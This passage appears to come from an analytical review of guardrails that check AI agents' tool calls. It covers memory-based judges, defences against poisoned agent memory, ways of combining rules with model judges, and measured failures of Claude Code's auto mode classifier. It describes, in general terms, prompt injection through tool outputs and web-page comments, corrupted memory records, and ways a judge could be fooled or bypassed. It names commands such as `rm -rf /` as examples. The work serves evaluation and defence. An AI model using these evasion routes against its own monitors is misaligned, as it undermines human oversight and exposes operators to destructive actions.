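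The starting accuracy of 70% is harder to explain. Yang doesn't name the judge that used the memory, but the description of the guard implies that it was Sonnet. In the main comparison, Sonnet got about 159 of all 189 external actions right. If it got only 69 of these 98 right, it must have got 90 of the other 91 right, while Opus got only 77 of those right. It seems more likely that the memory experiment used a different prompt or setup, in which the judge did worse than usual. If Sonnet had matched Opus on the other 91 actions in the main comparison, it would have got 82 of these 98 right without memory, the same number as with the guarded memory. The 13-point gain may therefore partly reflect a weak baseline.

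### Keeping stored and tested cases apart

A memory test is meaningless if the judge can find the answer to the case it is judging in its memory. Yang had the external set checked for overlap with the first version's material, but doesn't say how the memory experiment kept stored cases separate from the ones it tested.

The results suggest that the judge didn't simply retrieve each action's own entry. If it had, the memory with true verdicts would have put the right answer in the prompt, and accuracy should have been far above 79%. Retrieving an action's own entry also couldn't explain the gain from the guarded memory. That entry would only repeat the verdict Sonnet had given without precedents, so it couldn't correct a mistake.

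A more likely problem is that the memory contained actions very similar to the one being tested. If it was built from the rest of the 98 actions, its precedents came from the same collection and covered the same four subjects as the test. A new deployment starts with an empty memory, and the decisions it accumulates may include none as relevant.

In *Workerville* (2026), a judge assesses recorded episodes of agent behaviour using the three most similar human-labelled cases, each with its label, the reason for it and the supporting evidence. As a precaution, the system removes any entry with the same identifier as the episode under review before the search. This prevents an exact match but not a near-copy under another identifier.

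A stricter method is to have the guardrail decide each case using only what it has learned from earlier ones, and to let it store the new case only afterwards. This imitates real use, in which the guardrail has no access to later cases. *MEMBRANE* (Choi, Yang and colleagues, 2026) used this method for part of its evaluation.

### Storing an attack with its harmless counterpart

MEMBRANE also handles twins differently, because each entry in its memory describes an attack strategy, when to block a request, and which similar requests to allow. For example, an entry about using fictional or research stories to obtain weapons instructions also lists requests to brainstorm safety measures as allowed. For agents, an entry adds the kind of action involved and a condition under which that action is safe.

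SafeHarbor's pairs of prohibitions and exemptions are similar but prepared in advance, while MEMBRANE can keep adding entries from the attacks it encounters. After each pair of harmful and harmless requests, a model decides whether to create, change or delete an entry. Ordinary code rejects duplicate or wrongly formatted entries. When a new request arrives, MEMBRANE retrieves similar entries, and a model discards those that don't apply. A second model call then judges the request.

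Choi and colleagues tested this on AgentHarm, presenting its harmful tasks directly and in six disguised forms. The figures below are averages over all seven versions.

| Memory | Harmful tasks let through | Harmless tasks refused |
|---|---|---|
| Complete system | 25.9% | 6.3% |
| Without the paired conditions in each entry | 19.4% | 20.5% |
| Without learning from pairs | 28.3% | 26.2% |

Without the paired conditions, the guardrail caught somewhat more attacks but refused more than three times as many harmless tasks. A judge given only examples of attacks may start to classify anything similar as an attack, which would explain both changes. Learning from pairs helped with both kinds of error.

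In the test-then-learn experiment, Choi and colleagues withheld one type of attack while preparing the memory, then presented it as a stream of new requests. For attacks that used persuasive rewording, the share of harmful tasks let through fell from 73.9% to 34.5%. The share of harmless tasks refused rose from 5.1% to 17.0%, so even a memory with paired entries became stricter as it learned about the attack.

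In these experiments, the benchmark supplied a harmless counterpart for every attack. A deployed guardrail would have to find or write its own, and a badly chosen counterpart could teach it to allow an attack. MEMBRANE also judges the task before the agent begins, not each tool call. MEMBRANE may help a judge interpret requests, but the results don't show whether it could tell apart two uploads made during the same task.

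### Matching known attacks before calling a model

A verdict cache can still be useful against well-known attacks. *Spider-Sense* (Yu, Yang and colleagues, 2026) combines such a cache with precedents for less familiar cases.

Their system begins inside the agent. Its instructions tell it to watch for danger in the user's request, its own plan, its proposed actions and the results of its tools. If something looks suspicious, the agent wraps it in a special tag, which pauses the task and starts a check. The check has a separate bank of attack patterns for each of these four stages and works as follows:

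1. It turns the suspicious content into an embedding and computes its cosine similarity to every pattern in the relevant bank.
2. If the highest similarity exceeds a threshold, the check returns that pattern and its stored verdict at once.
3. Otherwise, it retrieves the closest patterns and a language model reasons about the content with those patterns as evidence.
4. The agent receives the result and decides whether to continue, stop or remove the dangerous part.

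The patterns describe strategies in general terms, such as hiding instructions in the comments of a web page, so a match doesn't depend on a particular address or file name.

Yu and colleagues tested the system on their own benchmark, which has attacks at all four stages and 153 harmless cases designed to resemble attacks. AGrail, the guardrail that keeps revising its checks, is included here for comparison.

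| Agent's model and protection | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless cases flagged | Time per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet alone | 35.2% | 51.4% | 30.5 s |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet with AGrail | 32.6% | 38.2% | 121.4 s |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet with Spider-Sense | 9.5% | 19.1% | 41.7 s |
| Qwen-max alone | 45.5% | 35.3% | 21.6 s |
| Qwen-max with AGrail | 33.0% | 24.9% | 103.9 s |
| Qwen-max with Spider-Sense | 13.6% | 10.4% | 23.4 s |

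Spider-Sense reduced both kinds of error with both models. The paper's summary lists the lowest attack success rate, the lowest false-positive rate and 8.3% extra time, but no single version achieved all three. The lowest attack success rate was with Claude, where the check increased running time by 37%.

When Yu and colleagues removed the reasoning step, protection and precision fell sharply. Removing the matching step left the system about as safe but much slower. So the cache mostly saves time on familiar attacks, and the model handles the rest, which fits Yang's finding that similarity alone isn't enough to decide semantic cases.

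The banks contain only attacks, so the model has no harmless precedents to compare with. This may have affected one case logged in the paper, in which a user asked an agent to upload the day's system logs to cloud storage. The agent tagged the upload and described it as an attacker's attempt to steal data. The closest stored pattern had a similarity of only 0.46, so the check passed the case to the model, which compared it with several data-theft patterns and classified it as probably harmful. The agent noted that the request looked like common practice and asked the user for details about the destination.

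The check flagged the upload that the user had requested, although Yu and colleagues present the case as a successful defence against a manipulated tool description. The agent had already assumed an attacker in its description, which made a resemblance to stored attacks more likely. Asking the user was reasonable, but a record of the company's own storage accounts might have made it unnecessary.

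Spider-Sense also depends on the agent to start the check. An agent that a prompt injection has already misled may detect nothing suspicious, in which case the memory is not consulted. A guardrail outside the agent avoids this weakness by checking every action, but it adds more delay.

### Protecting an agent's own memory

An agent may also keep a memory of earlier tasks to help it plan new ones. A corrupted record in that memory can lead the agent to propose a harmful action, but a separate guardrail can still block that action. A corrupted record in the guardrail's memory affects the check itself. Defences for the two kinds of memory therefore serve different purposes, even when they use similar methods.

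*A-MemGuard* (ICML 2026) protects an agent's memory against records that look harmless individually but cause trouble only in a particular situation. If the agent acts on such a record and saves the result as a success, the mistake becomes a precedent and makes further mistakes more likely. Yang's unchecked memory has a similar weakness, but there the errors come from the judge itself.

*Forgetting is Not Always Bad* (2026) describes A-MemGuard as a method that retrieves several related records and has a model reason from each one separately. It then scores how far each line of reasoning departs from the others and discards the records behind the outliers. Suppose an agent has five records about paying suppliers. If four lead it to verify the account number before paying and the fifth leads it to pay a new account immediately, A-MemGuard would discard the fifth.

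A-MemGuard also turns the faulty reasoning into a lesson, which it stores separately from the ordinary records. The agent consults these lessons before acting, so it can avoid repeating the mistake even if a similar record turns up again.

The A-MemGuard paper reports that the method reduced attack success rates by more than 95% with little loss of usefulness. This is a relative reduction, so an attack that had worked 60% of the time would work less than 3% of the time. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) reports that the method reduces throughput, the amount of work the agent gets through in a given time, by about 15%. That figure may not be dependable, because the survey describes a check made before a record enters the memory, while other accounts describe a comparison of retrieved records.

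Comparing records works only if there are enough good ones. *MemForm* (2026), which tested an adapted version of A-MemGuard, had to skip the comparison when only one record was available, because there was nothing to compare it with. If corrupted records become the majority, they form the consensus. *Your Agent's Memories Are Not Its Own* (2026) reports that A-MemGuard fails in that situation.

Yang's guard also relies on agreement, but between two models that assess the same case before it enters the memory. Corrupted records can't outvote them in the same way, but both models may make the same mistake. Based on the inferred counts, this happened for about two of the 61 accepted entries.

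A-MemGuard's consensus check would be a poor fit for a guardrail's precedents. Suppose the memory holds nine cases in which an engineer ran `kubectl get secret` to debug a program, and one in which an attacker used it to steal a password. The theft is the outlier, so the check might discard the only precedent showing that the command can be dangerous. Rare cases in an agent's store of working methods are often errors, but in a guardrail's memory they may be the most valuable entries.

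An entry can also be correct when two judges agree on it and become wrong later. For example, a precedent that allows uploads to a certain storage account becomes dangerous if the company gives up the account and someone else takes the name. *MemGuard* (2026), a separate system for agents' task memories, keeps a reward, a confidence score and usage statistics with every record, and uses them to merge, downgrade or retire records later. It outperformed the strongest earlier memory method in all 16 combinations of model and benchmark, and this later maintenance accounted for more of the gain than filtering records when they entered the memory. Those tests measured how many tasks agents completed, not how many attacks a guardrail caught. Yang's guard checks an entry only on admission, so an operator would need another way to find outdated precedents.

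## Combining rules and judges in one guardrail

Fixed rules are fast and predictable, while a judge can interpret a request or an unfamiliar command. An operator who combines them has to decide in advance which check runs first, which verdict counts when the two disagree, and what happens if the judge doesn't respond.

### Which verdict counts

In the more cautious arrangement, the judge can tighten a rule's verdict but never relax it, so the guardrail uses the stricter of the two verdicts. The order of the checks then affects only how much time and compute they take. Rules take a couple of milliseconds, so it makes sense to run them first and skip the judge for anything they block.

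With this arrangement, a dangerous action gets through only if both checks miss it, but a harmless one raises an alarm if either check flags it. If the checks make their errors independently, the combined rates are

FNR = FNR(rules) · FNR(judge)

FPR = 1 − (1 − FPR(rules)) · (1 − FPR(judge))

Suppose each check alone misses 10% of dangerous actions and flags 5% of harmless ones. If their mistakes are independent, a guardrail that flags an action when either check does will miss 1% of dangerous actions and flag almost 10% of harmless ones. In practice, two checks often make the same mistakes, and both rates then change less.

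The opposite arrangement sends the second check only the actions the first one flagged, and lets it clear them. The same two checks would then miss 19% of dangerous actions and flag 0.25% of harmless ones. An attacker would also gain more from fooling the second check. A judge misled by a prompt injection might let `rm -rf /` run if it can clear blocked actions, whereas if it can only make decisions stricter, the guardrail still does as well as the rules alone.

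When each check can only make a guardrail's decision stricter, false alarms add up, and a confidence threshold doesn't always remove them. *Parallax* (2026) describes a guardrail with several layers, including a small classifier trained to recognise the text of prompt injections. With every layer active, the guardrail blocked 18 of 50 legitimate actions. The classifier caused 14 of these blocks, all with a confidence of 1.00, so no threshold would have prevented them. In its default setup, the guardrail skips the classifier for the types of action the classifier tends to misjudge and sends them to a language model instead. This setup blocked none of the 50 actions.

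### When the judge doesn't answer

AgentTrust defaults to *review* after a failure, including when it can't parse the judge's answer. If the guardrail consults the judge on every unblocked action, a judge outage stops the agent at almost every step until a person approves it. This is safe, but it could tempt an operator to switch the guardrail off.

Yang gives this fallback verdict a confidence of 0.3, which could cause a problem with v2's confidence gate. If the gate treated the fallback like any other low-confidence verdict, it would discard the review, and an action that matched no rule would run. An attacker who could make the judge return an unreadable answer could exploit this. An implementation therefore has to handle a missing answer separately from an uncertain one.

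### AgentTrust's hybrids

In v1's standard procedure, the optional judge assesses only actions that the rules warn about or hold for review. Most semantic threats would never reach it, because an action that matches no rule gets the verdict *allow*. For the v1 experiments, Yang instead consulted a DeepSeek model on every action that the rules hadn't blocked, and used the stricter of the two verdicts. In the v2 hybrid, the judge can also only make the rules' verdict stricter, but v2 adds the confidence gate.

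| Version and test set | Check | Accuracy | FPR | FNR |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| v1, 300 actions | Rules | 95.0% | 2.3% | 5.4% |
| v1, 300 actions | Rules and judge, no gate | 88.0% | 9.0% | 0.8% |
| v1, 630 actions | Rules | 95.4% | 2.1% | 6.4% |
| v1, 630 actions | Rules and judge, no gate | 90.5% | 4.8% | 0.3% |
| v2, 630 actions | Rules | 95.4% | 2.1% | 6.1% |
| v2, 630 actions | Rules and gated judge (Sonnet 4.6) | 98.3% | 2.1% | 0.9% |
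| v2, external set | Rules | 48.1% | 22.4% | 52.9% |
| v2, external set | Rules and gated judge | about 78% | – | – |
| v2, external set | Judge alone (Opus 4.8) | 85.2% | 1.7% | 4.6% |

On the 300 actions, v1's judge caught six more of the 129 dangerous actions and flagged nine more of the 133 harmless ones. On the 630 actions, the judge caught 21 more dangerous actions and flagged only five more harmless ones, yet the number of correct verdicts fell by 31. At least 26 of the new errors must have been on actions that deserved a warning but got a stricter verdict. Harmless and dangerous actions are nearly equal in number in the first set, and dangerous ones are far more common in the second, so Yang's explanation that harmless actions outnumber dangerous ones in both sets can't be the main reason for the lower accuracy. An operator who worries mainly about missed attacks might reasonably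 choose this hybrid despite its lower accuracy.

The gate seems to have removed most of this side effect. On the 630 actions, the gated judge caught 18 more dangerous actions, and correct verdicts also rose by 18. The rules' four false alarms remained because the judge couldn't clear them. Yang reports the best result for each test set, which makes the hybrid look slightly better than it is, but the other three judges also reached at least 97.5%.

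Yang describes the gated judge as the "asymmetric" design proposed in the v1 paper, but the v1 design consulted the judge only when the rules gave a warning or a review. The v2 design depends on the judge's confidence, so it can also catch dangerous actions that match no rule. In a pilot of the v1 design on the 300 actions, Yang found that it kept about 80% of the reduction in misses with about 30% of the added false positives. The second figure is puzzling because, by Yang's definition, a warning on a harmless action is already a false positive, so making the warning stricter can't add another. The pilot may have used a different definition.

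On the external set, the rules raised about 13 false alarms, which the judge couldn't correct because it could only make verdicts stricter. The hybrid got 13 or 14 fewer verdicts right than Opus alone, so these false alarms could account for almost the whole gap.

Yang concludes that the judge should lead on unfamiliar actions and that its confident verdicts should override the rules. The reported results for this mode match those for Opus alone on all three measures, so the rules apparently added nothing. This mode also lets an attacker who fools the judge get past every rule. A possible compromise is to make a few rules final, such as the one against `rm -rf /`, and let the judge overrule the others.

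### How would a live system know which arrangement to use?

Yang calls this policy "distribution-aware". The rules' verdicts serve as a minimum when actions resemble those the rules were written for, and the judge's verdict takes precedence otherwise. But Yang gives no method for telling the two situations apart. The experiments distinguish them by which test set an action belongs to, a label that a live system doesn't have.

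The system could monitor how often the rules and the judge disagree. On the external set, Opus was right 37 percentage points more often than the rules, so they must have disagreed on at least 37% of actions. On the 630 actions, the same calculation gives a minimum of about 4%. A sudden rise in disagreement would be a useful warning, but someone would have to label a sample of actions to find out which check was wrong. One hundred harmless actions would usually be enough to distinguish a false-positive rate of 22% from one of 2%.

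A single switch for all traffic would still be crude. An agent may run familiar Git commands and an unfamiliar database tool in the same session, and on the external set the rules did far better on shell commands than on databases. An attacker might also flood the system with unusual actions to make it switch to the judge. Tracking errors for each rule would be more precise, because the system could stop relying on a rule that often flags harmless work and keep relying on the others. However, rules that rarely match would take a long time to assess.

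The rules would probably do worse on new traffic, even of a familiar kind, than on the 630 actions, because Yang had added rules in response to some of those actions.

### The replayed stream

Yang also simulated how AgentTrust v2 would change as it learned, using 30 streams of 1,500 actions each. During each stream, the system turned some of the judge's verdicts into rules and saved precedents that two judges agreed on to its memory.

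| Measure | Start | End |
|---|---|---|
| Actions sent to the judge | 50% | 44% |
| Accuracy on semantic actions | 71% | 80% |
| Accuracy on all actions | 84% | 85% |
| Harmless actions blocked | – | 0 in the whole run |

The simulation replayed verdicts that Yang had measured beforehand, with and without the memory, rather than having the judge assess these actions live. The results therefore show how the parts would interact if those measurements held, but not how a judge would respond to new actions.

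Overall accuracy hardly rose, which Yang attributes to the large share of actions that rules already handled correctly. But Yang also says 52% of the external set, which the stream seems to draw on, is semantic. If half the stream were semantic, a nine-point gain on semantic actions should have raised overall accuracy by more than four points. Either semantic actions were much rarer in the stream, or accuracy on the other actions fell. A fall would be a concern, because it could mean the learned rules did worse than the judge they replaced.

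Yang expects a larger saving in judge calls on real traffic, where most actions are harmless. That saving is doubtful if the learned rules only recognise attacks, because a harmless action would match none of them and still need a judge. To avoid those calls, the system also needs rules that identify safe actions.

The zero in the last row comes from a small set of actions. If the stream came from the external set, each of its 189 actions appeared about 240 times on average, and only about 58 of them were harmless. The replay used verdicts Yang had already measured, so repeating an action the judge hadn't blocked couldn't produce a block by the judge. Zero blocks among some 14,000 independent harmless actions would put the true rate below about 0.02%, but with 58 distinct actions the limit is about 5%.

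Yang nevertheless calls the absence of wrongful blocks a guarantee "by construction". The described design doesn't ensure this, because the gate lets a confident judge turn *allow* into *block*, and a confident judge can be wrong. Limiting the judge to warnings and reviews would guarantee that it never blocks a harmless action, but then every attack that only the judge recognises would run with a warning or wait for a person to review it. The rules could still block harmless actions.

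### Claude Code's auto mode

Claude Code's auto mode is a combined guardrail in wide use. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), it became the default for new sessions on individual and team subscriptions on 14 August. It handles a tool call as follows:

1. Permission rules run first. A built-in list allows tools that only read, and users can add their own rules. Auto mode ignores any user rule broad enough to allow arbitrary code, such as one that permits every `python` command.
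2. File edits inside the project run without a further check. Anthropic reasons that developers can review these edits through version control, which records every change.
3. A model, Claude Sonnet 4.6 in the original version, checks everything else. It first acts as a fast filter that answers only yes or no, with an instruction to err on the side of blocking.
4. If the filter flags the call, the same model receives the same input again, reasons about it step by step and gives the final verdict.

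The second stage, a slow reasoning step, runs only on the calls that the first-stage filter flags, so it can only relax the filter's verdict. This is the reverse of AgentTrust's arrangement, and it suits a filter that Anthropic deliberately made too strict.

Auto mode also has "hard denies", which cover actions such as sending secrets to an outside service. Anthropic designed the classifier never to approve these, even at the user's request. But a model decides whether an action falls into this category, so the block is less certain than one from a fixed rule.

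The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's own explanations so that the agent can't argue for a bad action, such as by claiming that the user had implicitly approved it. It also removes tool outputs because attackers' instructions usually enter through them. In Anthropic's tests, including both kinds of text made the classifier worse at catching overeager actions. Removing the user's messages as well gave the fewest misses, but the classifier then blocked things the user had plainly requested.

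Because of this choice, if an agent tries to cancel job `abc123` and the user never named it, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found that job in a list or made up the name. Anthropic accepts this limitation in return for better protection against prompt injection.

Anthropic reports the following error rates. The overeager actions come from real sessions in which an employee refused them or someone flagged them later.

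| Stage | Harmless calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Overeager actions missed (52) | Synthetic data thefts missed (1,000) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast filter | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Filter and reasoning | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The 17% miss rate comes from only 52 overeager actions, about nine of which were missed, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but accepted weak evidence of consent. In one example, a user said "Clean up the PR" (pull request), and the classifier treated this as permission to force-push, which overwrites the history of shared code.

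### What the error rates mean in 10,000 calls

A false-positive rate of 0.4% sounds negligible, but harmless calls vastly outnumber dangerous ones. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, of which 10 are dangerous. The share of alarms that are real is then

real share = 10 · (1 − FNR) / (10 · (1 − FNR) + 9,990 · FPR)

| Check | False alarms | Dangerous calls caught | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
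| Auto mode, fast filter only | 849 | 9.3 | 1% |
| Auto mode, both stages | 40 | 8.3 | 17% |
| AgentTrust v1, rules | 230 | 9.5 | 4% |
| AgentTrust v1, rules and ungated judge | 899 | 9.9 | 1% |
| AgentTrust v2, rules and gated judge | 210 | 9.9 | 5% |

The AgentTrust rows use the 300 actions for v1 and the 630 for v2. The two systems aren't directly comparable, because their test sets differ and Yang's false alarms include warnings, so it is more useful to compare rows within each system. Auto mode's reasoning stage avoids about 809 false alarms and lets one more dangerous call through. In AgentTrust v1, the ungated judge adds about 670 false alarms and catches half a dangerous call more. It is therefore worthwhile only if a miss is more than about 1,450 times as bad as a false alarm. That may be true if a false alarm is only a warning and a miss could destroy a company's database.

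Even with both stages of auto mode, about five of every six blocks would be mistakes. If only one of the 10,000 calls were dangerous, 98% of the blocks would be mistakes. Anthropic makes these mistakes less disruptive by returning the refusal to the agent, which can look for a safer method. After three refusals in a row or 20 in a session, auto mode stops the agent and asks the user.

### Comparison with human reviewers

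In a study described by Anthropic, 1,053 paid testers did coding work in a test environment. During each session, the experimenters replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it in 143 cases (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Auto mode blocked 800 commands that testers approved, and testers refused six that auto mode allowed, so requiring approval from both would have stopped only six more commands than auto mode alone.

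The testers were not protecting their own code, so they may have been less careful than usual. The commands were also clearly dangerous, which makes the study a poor test of semantic threats. The study counted only dangerous commands, so it can't show how many harmless ones either side would have stopped.

It does show how weak *review* verdicts can be if people receive too many of them. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. In ordinary use, people reject 3% of permission prompts but 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so they may pay more attention to rarer and more informative questions. AgentTrust sends uncertain cases to a person, so it depends on having few of them.

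Anthropic also commissioned a test of prompt injection in which none of 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But the average success rate was only 0.09% without the guardrail, so auto mode could hardly improve on it. Willison (2026), a software developer who writes about AI security, has asked for more independent confirmation.

### An independent test with ambiguous requests

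*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested auto mode on 128 routine maintenance requests, such as deleting old branches, cancelling jobs and restarting services. The requests varied in how clearly they named the target, how many targets they covered, and whether they concerned a production system. In one, the user writes, "my stale job for ticket 4812 could use attention", and the cluster also has a job with a very similar name that the agent must leave alone.

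A fixed policy used each request's ticket number, owner and environment to list the authorised targets. Claude Opus then labelled the agents' actions by comparing them with this list, and its labels matched a human's on 44 of 50 actions.

| Actions that change something | Unauthorised ones blocked | Authorised ones blocked |
|---|---|---|
| File edits, which skip the classifier | 0 of 51 | 0 of 42 |
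| Actions the classifier checked | 27 of 91 (30%) | 22 of 69 (32%) |
| All | 27 of 142 (19%) | 22 of 111 (20%) |

Auto mode therefore missed 81% of the unauthorised actions, compared with 17% in Anthropic's test. The unchecked file edits explain only a small part of the difference, since the classifier missed 70% of the unauthorised actions it did check. Many of the edits may be specific to this test. When agents couldn't find the usual command, they edited a local file such as `jobs.json`, which represented the system's state. On a real cluster, such an edit might not cancel anything, although many teams keep live system settings in project files.

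The choice of actions matters more. Anthropic's 52 actions went far enough beyond the user's request for someone to object. Ji and colleagues deliberately placed authorised and unauthorised targets side by side. They warn against comparing the two miss rates directly.

The 70% miss rate also understates the problem, because the classifier blocked authorised actions just as often as unauthorised ones. It therefore did no better on this test than blocking 30% of actions at random. This is the result one would expect if the classifier lacked necessary information. Telling two similar jobs apart requires information about who owns them, which is in the tool outputs that Anthropic removes.

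The classifier was stricter about production targets but not more accurate. Auto mode blocked 12% of unauthorised actions and 9% of authorised ones on low-risk targets, compared with 25% and 35% on production targets. It also seemed to respond more to the size of an operation than to ownership. It often allowed a precise deletion of someone else's branch but stopped a command with many targets. Anthropic lists a vague request to clean up old branches as a case that auto mode would block, but in this test it allowed 17 of 22 unauthorised actions on the branch tasks.

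Ji and colleagues tested the version available in April 2026. Anthropic has since given the classifier more facts about its surroundings, such as whether a code repository is public and whether a Git command would discard unsaved work. Anthropic says these and related changes reduced the miss rate from 12% to 7% in tests with synthetic attacks by Apollo Research, an AI safety company. This result supports giving a judge trusted facts from a program instead of raw tool outputs. But these facts still wouldn't show who owns a job.

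### Choosing enforcement by how precise the policy is

The researchers could compute the authorised targets with a fixed policy, so a rule with access to the list of jobs and owners could have made many of the decisions that auto mode left to a model. *From Alignment to Access Control* (Baracaldo, 2026) would favour such a rule, because it recommends deterministic enforcement whenever someone can state the policy precisely enough. A model is appropriate for vague policies, such as a ban on hateful speech.

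Baracaldo, a researcher at IBM, is especially critical of "Pretty Please" enforcement, in which a developer writes a precise policy into a model's prompt and hopes the model will follow it. In one of her examples, an agent deleted a production database despite clear instructions to change nothing. Access control could have prevented this, because "this agent may not write to the production database" is a precise policy.

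Yang's criterion would instead make the same case a semantic threat for a judge, because the command may be identical on a test database and no pattern in its text reveals the danger. The two criteria give the same answer for `rm -rf /`, which has both a clear pattern and a clear policy against it. Both also call for a judge when the policy is "read a secret only when the task requires it". But an operator can sometimes replace a vague policy with a precise one, such as "read payment secrets only with an approved ticket". This blocks some legitimate work, but it removes the need to infer the agent's purpose.

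Baracaldo's criterion is the better guide to choosing a mechanism because the operator controls the policy, whereas an attacker can change the text of an action. However, her paper is a conceptual analysis and doesn't test the criterion experimentally. A policy can also sound more precise than it is. One of her examples of a precise policy is to remove social security numbers and names with regular expressions, but names lack the fixed format of social security numbers, so a pattern would miss many names.

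Even a clear policy may depend on facts that the available rules can't check. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) examined security instructions in the files that developers write to guide Claude Code. It used a classifier to estimate that Claude Code's built-in permission rules could express only 16.6% of these instructions, and comparison with human labels suggested that this estimate was too high. For example, the permission rules can't fully enforce "Never commit secrets" because they match commands, file paths and domains, and can't inspect what a file contains. A program that scans files for known key formats could enforce part of this instruction, but recognising a password in an ordinary sentence might still require a model.
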